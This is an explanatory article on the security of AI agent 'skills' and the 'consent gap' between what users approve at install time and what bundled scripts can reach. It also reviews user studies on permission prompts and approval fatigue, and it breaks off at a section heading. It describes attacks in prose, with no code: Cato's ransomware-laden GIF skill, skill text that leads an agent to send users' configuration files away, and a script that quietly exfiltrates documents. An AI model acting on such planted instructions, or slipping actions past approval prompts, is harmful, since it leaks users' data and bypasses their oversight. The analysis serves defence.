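# Agent skills: user trust in their descriptions and the missing confinement of the code they run

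## What an agent skill is and whose authority it uses

An agent skill is a folder of written instructions, often with small programs, that an AI agent loads when a task seems to call for it. The agent is a language model connected to software, called the runtime, that lets it open files, run commands and call online services. Claude Code, Codex and OpenClaw are examples of runtimes. A skill gives the model know-how it lacks, such as how a particular company lays out its reports or how to fill in a PDF form, without retraining.

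Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, introduced the format on 16 October 2025 in *Equipping agents for the real world with Agent Skills* (2025) and published it as an open standard on 18 December. The next day the programmer Simon Willison (2025), in *Agent Skills*, called the specification "deliciously tiny" and "quite heavily under-specified". He guessed that it would end up with the Agentic AI Foundation, which the Linux Foundation had just set up to look after shared standards for agents. The Agentic AI Foundation (2026) announced Anthropic's donation of the format on 22 October 2026. *Towards Secure Agent Skills* (Li, Wu and colleagues, 2026), a security analysis written before that date, treats the handover as already complete. This seems to be a mistake, since the foundation started with three other projects (Agentic AI Foundation, 2025).

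Other companies adopted the format within months. By June 2026, the Agent Skills overview page listed 37 products that support it, including OpenAI's Codex, Google's Gemini CLI, Cursor and GitHub Copilot. The number of skills grew even faster. *Beyond Maliciousness* (Pandey, Singh and colleagues, 2026) cites one crawl that found 15,082 skills on a single marketplace in December 2025 and another that found 73,193 there a month later. A March 2026 count across three distribution platforms and GitHub found 238,180 unique skills.

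### The package

The standard explanations of the format all use a skill for handling PDF files. A cut-down version of such a skill has three files:

```
pdf-text/
├── SKILL.md
├── FORMS.md
└── scripts/
    └── extract.py
```

Only `SKILL.md` is compulsory. It opens with a header of labelled fields and continues in ordinary prose:

```
---
name: pdf-text
description: Extracts the text of PDF files and saves it as
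  plain text. Use when the user wants to search or summarise a PDF.
---
Run scripts/extract.py on the file that the user names.
Save the result next to the original.
If the PDF has a form to fill in, read FORMS.md first.
```

Agent Skills' *Specification* requires two header fields: a name of at most 64 characters and a description of at most 1,024. The description should cover what the skill does and when to use it. An author may add a licence, a free-text note on the environment the skill needs (such as network access), arbitrary metadata, and an experimental `allowed-tools` list of tools that the runtime may run without asking. The body of the file has no required format and may contain whatever helps the agent do the job.

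Nothing in the format ensures that these parts agree. The reference validator that Agent Skills offers authors checks that the header is well formed and that the name follows the naming rules, such as being in lower case. It does not compare the description with the prose under it, or either of them with `extract.py`. If its header and name were valid, a folder would pass whether its script extracted text or deleted files.

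### One request, start to finish

Suppose that a user has installed this skill along with twenty others, and asks the agent to summarise `invoice.pdf`.

When the session started, before the request arrived, the runtime searched its skill folders and put the name and description of every installed skill into the model's context, the text the model works from. Each entry takes up about 100 tokens (a token is a word or part of one), so even a large collection uses little room. At this stage the model had only the two header fields of the PDF skill.

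When a request comes in, the model picks a skill. According to the Agent Skills guide for developers of runtimes, most runtimes have no keyword matcher or other fixed rule for this and rely on the model's judgement of which description fits. Li and colleagues write the choice as a function *r*(*q*, *m*), where *q* is the user's request and *m* is the skill's name and description; the value is 1 if the model finds the skill relevant and 0 if it does not. The skill's author writes all of *m*, and no registry or verified identifier backs it. A person relies on the description to decide whether to install the skill, and the model later relies on it to decide whether to use the skill. Users can also bypass the model's choice by calling a skill by name, typically with a slash command.

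Having chosen, the model opens `SKILL.md` and the whole body enters the context. Agent Skills recommends keeping it under 5,000 tokens.

The model uses the other files last, and only those the task needs. The invoice has no form to fill in, so the model doesn't open `FORMS.md`. The model does need the invoice's text, so it issues a command such as `python scripts/extract.py invoice.pdf`, gets the text back, and writes the summary. The specification's name for this staged loading is progressive disclosure. It lets an author bundle long manuals or large tables with a skill without the model loading them for tasks that don't need them.

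Once a skill's body is loaded, the model seems to receive it as instructions to follow, and nothing in the format marks it as coming from a stranger. Li and colleagues go further than the official documents support when they hold that an activated skill stands at "operator level", with roughly the authority of the instructions that the company running the agent puts in the system prompt. The specification does not define the body's authority. In the simplest arrangement that the Agent Skills guide describes, only the descriptions are in the system prompt, and the body arrives as the result of an ordinary file read. Still, the guide advises developers to treat the body as lasting guidance, to keep it when the runtime trims old material from a long session, and to let the model read files in skill folders without a confirmation prompt. Li and colleagues also acknowledge that models differ in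 how they resolve conflicts between a skill and the user.

### A script that the model does not read

The model must read `SKILL.md` to follow it, but it needs only the file name to run a script such as `extract.py`. Anthropic's product documentation, *Agent Skills*, states that the agent receives only the script's output and that the code "never enters the context window".

Anthropic chose this design for good reasons. A sorting program uses far less computation than a model that sorts a list by writing it out word by word, and it gives the same result each time. Anthropic's launch post describes a PDF skill with a Python script that finds all the form fields in a document. The agent can run the script without loading either the script or the PDF into its context. If the model had to read the source on every run, much of this efficiency would be lost.

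The drawback is that the model sees only what a bundled script prints. For example, one version of `extract.py` might extract the invoice's text and print it, while another does the same and also sends a copy of the invoice to a server that the author controls. Both print identical text, so the model's context is identical and it has no basis for telling the user that anything went wrong. When a model writes its own code for a task, the session's record includes that code for the user or a monitoring program to inspect, but with a bundled script the record contains only a command line and a result.

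This is the default behaviour, and a runtime or user can change it. The source is in a folder that the model can open, and a cautious user could tell the agent to read every script before running it. Anthropic notes that code in a skill can also serve as documentation, and asks authors to make clear whether the agent should run a file or read it. But reading a script does not limit what the script can do once it starts.

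### Whose access the script uses

The environment in which the runtime starts a script determines what the script can access. On an ordinary personal computer without extra protection, any program the user launches can open whatever the user's account can open. This includes the runtime and any script it launches. `extract.py` can therefore read the invoice, the user's other documents, the keys used to log in to remote servers, and any passwords or access tokens in the runtime's settings. It can also reach the internet. According to Anthropic, skills in Claude Code have the same network access as any other program on the computer.

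The user's account already had all of this access, including to those keys, before the skill was installed. Installation can be as simple as copying a folder. Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Skills* tells Claude Code users that they can add a skill by hand to a directory in their home folder. According to Pandey and colleagues, installing a skill gives it standing to direct the agent, but no privilege that the session did not already have. A stranger's instructions and code can now influence how the agent uses the account, which creates the consent gap between what the user thought they were approving and what the skill can do.

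Hosted runtimes can confine a skill's code much more tightly. When a developer uses skills through Anthropic's programming interface, the scripts run in a walled-off container on Anthropic's servers, with no network access and no way to install further packages. On claude.ai, scripts may have full, partial or no network access, depending on the settings. OpenAI's interface for developers accepts skills in both hosted and local containers, according to The Decoder's *OpenAI upgrades Responses API with features built specifically for long-running AI agents*. OpenAI's toolkit for building agents also keeps credentials out of the environment where model-generated code runs, according to Help Net Security's *OpenAI updates Agents SDK, adds sandbox for safer code execution* (2026). In Microsoft's agent framework, a skill's scripts run only once the developer supplies a component to run them.

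So the same folder may be nearly harmless in one place and able to read a user's whole home directory in another. Li and colleagues make the same point about Claude Code and Anthropic's hosted interface, and add that Claude Code has since gained optional isolation modes. They conclude that where a skill runs and what it can reach depend on the deployment, which seems right. A user therefore cannot learn from the author's description or the specification how much is at risk. Even in a container, a script still has the invoice and could return text with the bank account number changed.

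### Five terms from computer security

Security researchers had a vocabulary for this situation long before there were agents.

*Ambient authority* is access that code has only because of the account or process it runs in. `extract.py` can read the user's login keys because the user can, even though nobody decided that it should. The script only has to name a file, and the operating system checks the account's rights to that file without considering the script's purpose.

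*Least privilege* is the principle that a program should have only the access its job needs. For the request above, the script needs to read `invoice.pdf`, write one text file, and load the Python libraries it depends on. It needs no network access or keys. But other requests need different access. The sample skill that Li and colleagues print may read any PDF in the working directory, merge several files, and download PDFs from the web first. It needs the network when the user pastes in a web address, but not when the user wants a local invoice summarised. A single list of permissions that is fixed at installation and covers every request will therefore grant more access than most requests need.

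A *capability*, in this vocabulary, is a specific right to use a specific resource in a specific way. The word has nothing to do with how able a model is. Suppose that the runtime opens `invoice.pdf` itself, for reading only, and passes the open file to the script. The script now holds a right to that one document, where before it had a name and the whole account's power to act on names. (Pandey and colleagues use "capability" differently, for any action that a skill's files suggest it may perform, such as running shell commands. Theirs is a measure of reach and confers no right.)

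Giving the script a capability achieves little if it keeps its ambient authority, because it can ignore the open file and look for the keys. *Confinement* is the guarantee that, while code runs, something outside it prevents it from using any resource beyond the capabilities it was given. The guarantee must also cover any helper program that `extract.py` starts, or the script could use that program to steal the keys. Software that enforces these limits, usually with the operating system's help, is called a sandbox.

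A *confused deputy* is a program that holds authority from one party and ends up using it for another. In the PDF example, the deputy is the agent. Suppose the skill's author adds a line to `SKILL.md` telling the agent to attach the user's configuration files to an error report whenever extraction fails. The agent reads those files with the user's rights and sends them off for the author's benefit, even if the script contains nothing malicious. A script that steals keys by itself is a different failure because it involves no deputy. Confining the script prevents neither the misuse in this example nor a similar one that starts with the script's output. Even a perfectly confined `extract.py` returns text to the model, and if that text contains instructions, the model may act on them with access that the script never had.

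### What earlier formats constrained

Skills came after two other ways of extending a language model, and both held authors to more.

ChatGPT plugins, which OpenAI offered from 2023 to 2024, ran on the plugin provider's servers, not on the user's machine. The provider published a typed interface, a machine-readable list of operations and the kind of input each one accepted. The model could call only the operations on that list. A PDF plugin, for example, would have had an operation like "extract text" that took a file address as input. OpenAI reviewed each plugin before it entered the store, and users switched plugins on for one conversation at a time. The provider could still misuse any documents the model sent, but it could not access the login keys on the user's disk.

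The Model Context Protocol (MCP), which Anthropic released in November 2024, is a standard way to connect AI applications to outside tools. Before it, connecting *M* applications to *N* tools could take up to *M* × *N* separate integrations. An MCP server declares its tools with typed inputs, which limit the calls the model can make but not what the server's code does when it handles them. The server may run on the user's computer with the user's access, and no store has to review it first. An unconfined local MCP server for PDFs therefore has the same ambient authority as `extract.py`.

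Skills also dropped the typed interface. The model now follows prose, which may direct it to do anything the runtime permits, and the skill author's instructions reach it in the same form as any other text. This comparison follows the account of the three mechanisms by Li and colleagues, who rate each mechanism on four properties fixed by its design: the form of the instructions, the separation of instructions from data, the declaration of needed resources, and the trust a user extends on enabling the extension. They rate plugins as protected on all four and skills as exposed on all four. These ratings are the researchers' judgements and are not based on measured rates of harm. Plugins also had the advantage that a single company ran both the interface and the store.

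In exchange, skills are easier to write than plugins and can express more. A plugin required a formal interface description and could not express a multi-step procedure. Li and colleagues blame those limits for the plugins' low uptake, and OpenAI shut plugins down on 9 April 2024. Anyone who can write clear instructions can write a skill, and the skill can include informal knowledge that does not fit a list of typed operations, such as which of two forms to use, what to check before sending, and when to stop and ask. Authors can also combine skills with MCP, as Anthropic suggested at launch, by writing a skill that teaches the agent a workflow using MCP tools.

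According to Li and colleagues, skills differ from both predecessors in that nobody can verify the isolation around a skill, because it has no binding declaration. A runtime may put `extract.py` in a sandbox, but the author never had to state which files and connections the script needs, so neither the user nor an auditing program can tell whether the sandbox is tight enough. Anthropic accordingly advises users to treat a skill like software they are about to install, take it only from a source they trust, and look through every file in the folder first.

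## What a user approves and what the skill receives

Someone who installs the sample skill `pdf-text` agrees to roughly what its description says, which is extracting text from PDF files. The agent that follows the skill can do far more. Li and colleagues call the difference between these two sets of actions the consent gap.

In their notation, *A* is the set of all actions open to the agent, such as reading and writing files, connecting to the network and starting other programs. *D* is the part of *A* that the skill declares, which they take to be whatever its description states or its optional header fields name. The user agrees to *D* at installation, and also to the contents of `SKILL.md` if they read it. After that, the skill can direct the agent to take any action in *A*. The consent gap, written *A* ∖ *D*, is the set of actions in *A* that are not in *D*.

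For `pdf-text`, *D* contains little more than reading a PDF and saving a text file. On an unprotected laptop, *A* ∖ *D* includes reading the user's login keys, deleting their photographs and uploading their tax returns. In a hosted container, both *A* and *A* ∖ *D* are much smaller.

Nobody could compute this difference for a real skill, because a description is a sentence or two of prose and does not list exactly which actions it covers. "Extracts the text of PDF files" does not mention loading a Python library, though any user would accept that. It also does not rule out sending the file to an online text-recognition service, which some users would object to. Li and colleagues concede that the description is too weak a specification to check the instructions against.

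According to Pandey and colleagues, a user who installs a skill by copying its folder into place is asked to approve nothing beyond the copy itself.

Pandey and colleagues also estimated how much of *A* published skills use. In July and August 2026 they scanned 6,309 listings from two marketplaces, skillsmp and ClawHub. A language model read every file in each listing and noted what the skill appeared able to do. Half the listings showed signs of running shell commands, 35% of reading files, 31% of writing files, 31% of sending data over the network and 13% of using credentials. Most of these skills probably have ordinary reasons for doing so, since only about one listing in twenty looked malicious. The figures are a model's inferences from the files, and the sample excludes the most popular skills and those hardly anyone uses. Still, they suggest that a typical skill uses a good deal of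 the agent's access, and Pandey and colleagues find that users can see almost none of this when they install a skill.

### What widens the gap

Li and colleagues identify three properties of the approval that widen the gap. First, the approval lasts, so a user who installs `pdf-text` in March sees no new approval prompt when the model picks the skill in June.

The approval also applies equally to all actions, from extracting text to deleting a folder, no matter how far-reaching or hard to undo they are.

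Finally, a user's approval still applies after the skill changes, because it attaches to the skill's identity and not to a particular version of its files. According to Anthropic's documentation, Claude Code watches the folders where skills are stored and picks up edits to `SKILL.md` during a running session. When someone on a Team or Enterprise plan edits a skill they have shared with colleagues, the colleagues "automatically get the updated version at next use", according to Anthropic's *Use skills in Claude*. If a colleague also signs in to Claude Code with the same account, the program checks for new versions about every ten minutes while they work. But when a company publishes skills through a review process, everyone stays on the approved version until a reviewer accepts the next one.

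These properties follow from what the specification leaves out, so a runtime can do better, and some do. A skill's effects can also persist after its folder is deleted. Many agents read standing instructions at startup from files such as `CLAUDE.md` or `AGENTS.md`. Li and colleagues point out that a skill able to write files can edit these, and then affect sessions in which the model never chooses the skill.

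### The MedusaLocker demonstration

In December 2025, the security company Cato Networks published a test of what a skill can do after a single approval. *From Productivity Boost to Ransomware Nightmare* (Cherny, 2025) describes how the company's team added one short function to the GIF-making skill that Anthropic publishes as open source. The function appeared to tidy up the finished GIF, but it actually downloaded and ran another program. In the test, that program was MedusaLocker, working ransomware that encrypts a victim's files so that an attacker can demand payment for them.

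The team ran Claude in its strictest security mode. The user saw a skill for making GIFs and code that looked safe. Anthropic's software also warns before a skill runs that "Claude may use instructions, code, or files from this Skill." The user approved, and the skill's main script started. The added function then downloaded and launched the ransomware, which encrypted the files on the test machine. No prompt appeared for the download, the launch or the encryption, and Cherny reports no warnings or log entries for them either.

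The prompts stopped because the runtime can prompt the user only about commands that the agent issues. Once a command starts a program, that program and anything it starts deal with the operating system directly. The user's approval of the GIF script therefore allowed everything the script went on to do.

Axios' *Researchers trick Claude plug-in into deploying ransomware* (2025) adds that Claude had reviewed the visible code in the skill before running it. Models often run bundled scripts without reading them, so Claude was more careful here than usual, but the review still failed because the ransomware was not in the folder.

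Cato ran all of this in a controlled environment, and there were no victims. Li and colleagues list it as a documented incident and write of "users" who approved the skill, but Cherny mentions no users outside the test. She describes one run from approval to encryption, which is good evidence that a single approval covers very different actions. She also claims that an approved skill keeps its permissions permanently, which one run cannot establish.

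The technique isn't specific to skills either, since any downloaded script with the same function would behave the same way. With a skill, though, the user asked for a GIF and may not think of themselves as running a stranger's program. Cherny complains that the prompts made this worse by creating "a false sense of safety".

Cato reported the problem to Anthropic on 30 October 2025, two weeks after skills launched. Anthropic replied that skills are meant to execute code, that users see a question and a warning before the code runs, and that "it is the user's responsibility to only use and execute trusted Skills." It later gave Axios the same answer. Cherny agrees that running code is integral to the design, so the two sides disagree only about how much a user's approval should cover. Anthropic's warning is accurate, but it is the same for the original GIF skill and the altered one, so it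 doesn't help the user tell them apart.

### Why reading SKILL.md does not close the gap

Cato's change was to the skill's code. A user who read every word of `SKILL.md` would have found ordinary instructions for making GIFs.

The description is even less informative, partly because the model also uses it to pick a skill. Anthropic tells authors whose skill never triggers to check that the description clearly explains when to use it. An author can follow this advice without listing the files the skill opens or the servers it contacts. The user then makes a security decision based on text written to help a model choose between tools, and nothing compares that text with the code.

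Reading the scripts as well is much better. A programmer who noticed the added function in the GIF skill would have seen an image tool downloading and running a program for no good reason. Anthropic's review checklist for companies, in *Skills for enterprise*, includes searching for this kind of network call. So a reviewer could have caught the altered skill, but only if they could read Python.

Even a skilled reader can't fully check a skill by reading its folder. Content that the skill fetches from a remote server isn't in the folder, and it can change later. Anthropic itself warns that trustworthy skills can become compromised when their external dependencies change. The prose is also hard to audit because, as Li and colleagues point out, inspecting a skill does not reveal everything it will lead a model to do across all the requests the model might receive.

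### The argument over trusted sources

Anthropic responds to these risks with advice to users in its current developer documentation: "Use Skills only from trusted sources: those you created yourself or obtained from Anthropic." In the December 2025 version, from around the time of the Cato report, Anthropic "strongly" recommended the same thing and told anyone who had to use an unknown skill to audit it thoroughly.

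There is a reasonable case for this position, since broad access is much of what makes skills useful. A skill that posts a weekly report to a company's chat system would be safe in Anthropic's hosted interface, but it wouldn't work because scripts there cannot reach the network. People have also run downloaded programs with the full permissions of their accounts for decades, on much the same advice, and a runtime cannot determine which permissions a new skill legitimately needs.

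The comparison with installing software is less comforting than it sounds because not all software is confined. Pandey and colleagues contrast skills with Android apps and browser extensions, where developers must request permissions and the system blocks whatever they have not requested. Users of those systems also have to trust publishers, but only within the limits the system enforces. An unconfined skill is more like a program downloaded from a website.

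Taken literally, the rule excludes nearly everything on the skill marketplaces, as well as skills written by colleagues, which Anthropic's own products help people share. Anthropic's other guidance is looser. Its help page counts a colleague as a possible "less-trusted source" whose skills the user should review before enabling them, and its enterprise guide requires the same review for internal contributors as for third parties. In practice, Anthropic seems to be advising users to audit any skill that neither they nor Anthropic wrote.

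The strict version would have prevented the Cato attack, provided that the user downloaded the GIF skill from Anthropic's own repository. Someone who met the altered copy through a link on social media would have had a harder time, since it was Anthropic's skill in almost every line. To apply the rule they would need to know who had published that copy, and there is little to go on:

- No marketplace ties publication to a verified identity, according to Li and colleagues. One accepted uploads from any account more than a week old.
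- Anyone can call their skill "verified" or "official", and whether somebody checks depends on the marketplace, as ramimac.me's *Agent Skill Supply Chain Risks* notes. Skill names are not reserved to their owners, so a copy can use the original's name.
- Attackers can inflate download counts and ratings, and they can take over the account of an honest author.

Anthropic's developer platform rejects skill names that contain "anthropic" or "claude", which stops the crudest impersonation there. The rule doesn't prevent impersonation of other publishers, and it doesn't apply to folders that users copy from elsewhere.

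Even if users knew and trusted a skill's publisher, the skill could still put their data at risk, because an honest author can write a script that reads too many files or sends a document to a service the user would not have chosen. Pandey and colleagues judged about a quarter of the listings to carry serious exposure, roughly five times the share that looked malicious.

The alternative is to audit the skill. In its enterprise guide, Anthropic asks reviewers to read every file, run the scripts in a sandbox to confirm that their output matches the description, look for network calls and hidden instructions, and repeat the review for each update. No single step is enough. The version of `extract.py` that secretly sends the invoice away would pass the output check, so the reviewer would have to catch it by finding the network call. A company with a security team can do this work, but it is hard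 to imagine a person who wants one GIF doing it.

Anthropic has since taken on some of the vetting itself. Its *Get started with skill and plugin scanning* describes an automated check that blocks third-party skills it finds malicious. Anthropic turned the check on by default for Enterprise organisations that had not chosen a setting before 2 October 2026. It skips skills installed before scanning began and those uploaded through the developer interface. Anthropic says a pass "isn't a guarantee that a skill is safe in every respect", and that the scan will not catch a skill that misbehaves but isn't malicious.

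Telling users to install skills only from trusted sources is sound advice for lowering risk, but it doesn't justify treating their approval as informed. Most users can follow the advice only by refusing nearly every skill that other people write.

### Where a runtime still asks

The gap is narrower where a runtime asks the user for further approval after installation. According to Google's *Managing Agent Skills*, Gemini CLI asks the user to confirm the source when they install a skill from a remote address, and asks for a new approval every time the model tries to activate a skill. Google's overview of the feature says the second prompt shows the skill's name, its purpose and the folder it will gain access to. The user can still only accept or refuse the whole request, and the stated purpose presumably comes from the skill's author.

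According to Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode*, Claude Code in Manual mode stops to ask the user before most actions that edit files, run shell commands or reach the network. If `SKILL.md` tells the agent to upload the user's configuration files, the user sees the upload command and can refuse it, so they have a second chance to reject something in *A* ∖ *D*.

Claude Code runs a fixed set of read-only commands without asking, including the one that prints a file's contents, unless the user restricts reading outside the project. For a bundled script, the permission prompt shows a command such as `python scripts/extract.py invoice.pdf` but not what the script will do. If the user chooses not to be asked again, Claude Code saves a rule for later sessions in the same repository, according to Anthropic's documentation. The rule matches the text of the command, so it should still allow the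 command if the skill's author later rewrites `extract.py`.

A skill's author can also remove prompts by listing tools in the header field `allowed-tools`. According to Anthropic's documentation for Claude Code, the field pre-approves the listed tools, and every other tool remains callable. This contradicts Li and colleagues, who describe the field as a restriction that some runtimes honour and others ignore. An author can use it to let a bundled script run without any prompt, and Anthropic warns that a skill "can grant itself broad tool access". The permission lapses when the user sends their next message. So the only machine-readable part of *D* removes prompts without reducing *A*. Pandey and colleagues found the field in only 770 of 6,061 listings with a readable header, and 59% of those 770 understated what the skill's files could do.

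Most users of Claude Code may not see these prompts. Since version 2.1.283, Anthropic starts interactive sessions in the terminal and in the VS Code editor in auto mode, where a second model reviews actions in place of the user. To justify the change, Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* cites the company's own tests, in which auto mode did at least as well as manual review on every measure, and the finding that users approve 97% of the prompts they see. The second model may well stop an upload that a tired user would have approved. But a user who keeps the default settings makes fewer decisions after installation, so more depends on what they understood when they installed the skill.

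## How people answer an agent's permission requests

Users accept a whole skill once, at installation, and may later approve or refuse single actions that the agent proposes while following it. The user studies described below cover only these later decisions, so any conclusion drawn from them about installation is an inference.

People who approve an action can compare it with the task they have in mind. When they install a skill such as `pdf-text`, they have only the author's description and no specific task yet, such as reading an invoice. But installations are rare, while permission prompts can arrive so often that people stop reading them.

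### When agents ask and how long an answer lasts

In *How Agents Ask for Permission*, Michael and Roesner (2026) reviewed 21 proposed permission systems and, in May and June 2026, tried five commercial products: the Claude and ChatGPT chatbots, ChatGPT's agent mode (which operates a remote browser), and the desktop agents Claude Cowork and Codex. Their categories cover how users state their wishes and how software enforces them, but their observations also show that interfaces differ widely in when permission prompts appear, what they show and how long a grant lasts.

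The ChatGPT chatbot asked before every action that needed a permission, and users could not approve any in advance. ChatGPT's agent mode never asked, even before opening Gmail. Codex asked by default, and users could have a model review actions for them, but only for all tools in the session at once. In the Claude chatbot, users could set each permission to "Always allow", "Blocked" or "Needs approval". Even with "Needs approval" set, Claude sometimes created an email draft without asking. Claude's explanation was that it had inferred permission from the request, though this may not be reliable. Michael and Roesner reproduced the behaviour at least three times and reported it to Anthropic on 2 July 2026.

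Many permission prompts name only a tool. *Options, Not Clicks* (Li, Khabra and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who clicks "Always Allow" when an agent uses a file-search tool, connected through MCP, on a sales folder, and thereby also allows it to search their whole home directory. Claude Code prints commands, which are more specific but help only users who can read them. Researchers have tried prompts that describe the consequence in plain words, such as buying a $25 airport lounge pass.

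A permission may last for one action, for a session, or until the user withdraws it, and withdrawing it can be hard. In Claude Cowork, a new session started without the permissions of earlier ones, but an old session still had them when the user reopened it. The only ways Michael and Roesner found to revoke a folder permission permanently were to use the operating system's own controls or uninstall the app. Only six of the 21 research proposals clearly let users change or withdraw a permission later. The approval a user gives by installing a skill has no end date.

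### Approval fatigue

People who answer many similar prompts tend to stop reading them, which researchers call approval fatigue. Anthropic seems to be the only developer that has published how often its users approve permission prompts. According to its *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, users accepted 93% of Claude Code's prompts. The company later cited 97%.

Users who read every request carefully could still produce these approval rates, because most commands that a coding agent proposes are harmless. If one request in a thousand were dangerous, a user who refused only the dangerous ones would approve 99.9% of requests, and a user who refused nothing would approve 100%. Anthropic points out that users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents, so they are willing to say no, but people reject plans for many reasons besides safety.

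An experiment by Anthropic measures attention more directly. The company hired 1,053 testers for a coding study in a test environment. The testers knew they were being evaluated, but not on what. Partway through each session, one permission prompt displayed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

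Anthropic was testing a product it wanted to make the default, and testers risked less with somebody else's code than developers do with their own. The decline over a session is harder to dismiss, because everyone compared worked in the same artificial setting.

Many users also remove prompts through their settings. In June 2026, 5% of active users of Claude Code's terminal version had a rule allowing any shell command. Another 43% had rules allowing interpreters such as Python or Node, and Anthropic considers these rules almost as broad. In Manual mode, a rule allowing any Python command would let `extract.py`, or any other Python script in a skill, start without a prompt. A quarter of interactive sessions began with permission checks bypassed.

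Software practitioners describe a similar loss of attention. In *Let the Agent Do It?*, Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) interviewed 18 practitioners who use AI agents and then surveyed 115, of whom 107 answered the questions on permissions. Just under half of the 107 said they read requests carefully, a third said they skim them, and a fifth said they approve by default. A third said they had become less careful over time. One interviewee worried about permissions at first but said that after many similar requests, "I stopped caring". These are self-reports, and practitioners probably pay less attention than they say.

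The same survey suggests that people focus on requests that look risky. Three quarters said they check requests to write, delete or gain higher privileges more closely, and 98% were more willing to grant read-only access than other kinds. Yet 62% said they would never let an agent have sensitive data. These preferences conflict when a read permission covers a whole home directory, which also contains login keys.

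Repeated approval is weak evidence that a user trusts an agent or wants it to do the same thing again. Salerno and colleagues argue that users can also approve requests out of habit, tiredness or time pressure, and they warn designers against treating past approvals as stable preferences. A user who was right to approve one action may also be wrong to approve the next if it reaches more files or is harder to undo.

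### Sharing data that a task does not need

Even attentive users have to judge what a task requires. Wu, Yang and colleagues (2025), in *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents*, tested this judgment with 205 people in the United States, two of whom they excluded for invalid responses. Participants imagined training a personal assistant and answered 20 questions about which data it could share with which tools. They could choose to share always, share this once, refuse this once or never share. In five of the questions, the researchers added data that the task did not need.

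The set-up encouraged caution. Participants first answered questions about their attitudes to privacy, and every permission question warned that the agent or its tools might collect unnecessary data. Even so, only 3% of participants never shared anything unnecessary, and nobody gave the right permission every time. Adding unnecessary data to the requests did make some people more cautious, raising the proportion who used "never share" at least once from 68% to 79%.

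Participants had also picked out the data they thought the assistant would need. They shared unnecessary data about 78% of the time when they wrongly believed it was needed, and still shared it about 38% of the time when they correctly saw that it wasn't.

Wu and colleagues conclude that many users believe an agent even when it is wrong, but the participants may instead have had their own mistaken ideas about what the tools needed. The researchers also used their own list to judge which data was necessary, so some of the "unnecessary" sharing may have been reasonable. Sharing also depended on how sensitive the data seemed. People withheld social security numbers in 46% of cases where the task required them, but freely shared harmless-sounding items such as the name of a workspace.

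The researchers used these answers to build a model that predicts which permissions a user will grant. Its predictions matched participants' choices 85.1% of the time, and 94.4% for its highest-confidence predictions. These figures measure agreement with users, so a model trained on the choices of people who over-share would presumably over-share for them.

### Rules written in advance

If permission prompts tire people out, users could instead set rules before the agent starts. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) compared this approach with two others. The 113 participants, none from the software industry, supervised a simulated assistant through a day of emails, a trip to the airport and tidying up afterwards. The assistant proposed 18 actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had asked for, such as reading private messages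 or adding travel insurance.

One group approved or refused each action. For the second group, a model allowed some actions and passed the rest, including all seven unrequested ones, to the participant. The third group wrote four rules beforehand, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting things, and accessing private information.

| | Approved every action | Model reviewed first | Wrote rules |
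|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Participants | 34 | 44 | 35 |
| Prompts per person | 18.0 | 10.0 | 10.9 |
| Unrequested actions blocked | 59.6% | 53.9% | 39.6% |
| Approval rate when prompted about an unrequested action | 40.3% | 46.1% | 66.8% |
| Time spent on rules and prompts | 142 s | 120 s | 129 s |

People who wrote rules blocked the smallest share of unrequested actions. After statistical adjustment, their share was 20 percentage points lower than that of people who decided on each action separately, and 14.5 points lower than that of the model-review group. The 14.5-point difference was no longer statistically significant after Yan corrected for multiple comparisons.

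Participants chose "ask" for 114 of the 140 rules, which left those decisions to prompts, and they then approved most of the prompts. Of the 148 unrequested actions that went ahead in this group, participants had approved 133 by hand. For private information, "never" would have blocked two unrequested actions and nothing useful, yet only 10 of 35 people chose it and 23 chose "ask". They could not know this in advance, so it was reasonable to keep the option open.

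It is unclear why this group approved more. Its members saw prompts only where they had chosen "ask", so the approval rates compare slightly different sets of people. This difference can't explain the whole result, because the group blocked less overall even counting its "never" rules as blocks. Yan also added participants to this group after random assignment ended, and no one's real money or messages were at risk.

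People in Yan's study who were asked to approve or refuse every action refused about 60% of the unrequested ones. In Anthropic's experiment, only 13.6% of testers refused a dangerous command. Yan's participants saw only 18 prompts, in plain language, and more than a third of the actions were unrequested. Anthropic's testers had to spot one dangerous command in a longer series of technical ones. This suggests that wording and frequency matter a great deal, but the studies differ in too many ways to tell how much each contributes.

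Enforcing a user's "never" requires software that can identify which actions it covers. Yan built a separate prototype that sorts tools into categories from their names, descriptions and input formats. With a simulated "never" rule, it failed to stop 14% of the tools it should have stopped. The prototype relies on text that the tool's author writes, just as a skill's author writes its description. Yan did not test the prototype on deliberately misleading text.

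### Bounded choices in place of repeated clicks

"Allow once" leads to more prompts, while "Always Allow" grants too much access. ConLeash, a program by Li, Khabra and colleagues that sits between an agent and its MCP tools, offers intermediate choices. When the agent tries to search a file for prices, the user can allow searches of only that file or of the whole sales folder. If the user allows the folder, later searches inside it run without a prompt, but a search of the home directory triggers a new one.

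ConLeash describes each call by a boundary with four parts: where the input comes from, where the output goes, how sensitive the data is, and what effects the call has. A new call may run under an earlier approval if its boundary is no broader than the approved one in any of the four parts. Permission to read a folder therefore doesn't extend to deleting or emailing its files. A language model works out the four parts and can misjudge them, but ConLeash compares boundaries by fixed rules.

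Sixteen people tried ConLeash. Before the test, three said they read prompts carefully, and 13 said they used "Always Allow" to make prompts go away. Each participant did three tasks with ConLeash and three with ordinary tool-level prompts, and the researchers varied the order and which tasks went with which interface. With ConLeash, 46.3% of decisions were lasting permissions, compared with 13.3% under the ordinary prompts. ConLeash's lasting permissions were much narrower, however, and let 41.9% of tool calls run without a further prompt. Fifteen participants preferred ConLeash and one had no preference.

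Participants could also state absolute limits in their own words, such as never sending a tax form to anyone else. ConLeash correctly enforced 45 of the 48 limits they wrote. The other three, such as "don't touch my photos", were too vague for it to interpret.

The study is good evidence that people will accept narrower permissions when an interface offers them. It is weaker evidence on safety, because the main results count what people granted, not how many harmful actions they refused when a new prompt appeared. People may pay more attention to a prompt that appears only when something has changed, but a short session with 16 people cannot show whether that lasts. ConLeash also checks only tool calls, so if a call starts a skill's script, ConLeash cannot directly monitor the files that the script then opens.

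### Automated reviewers

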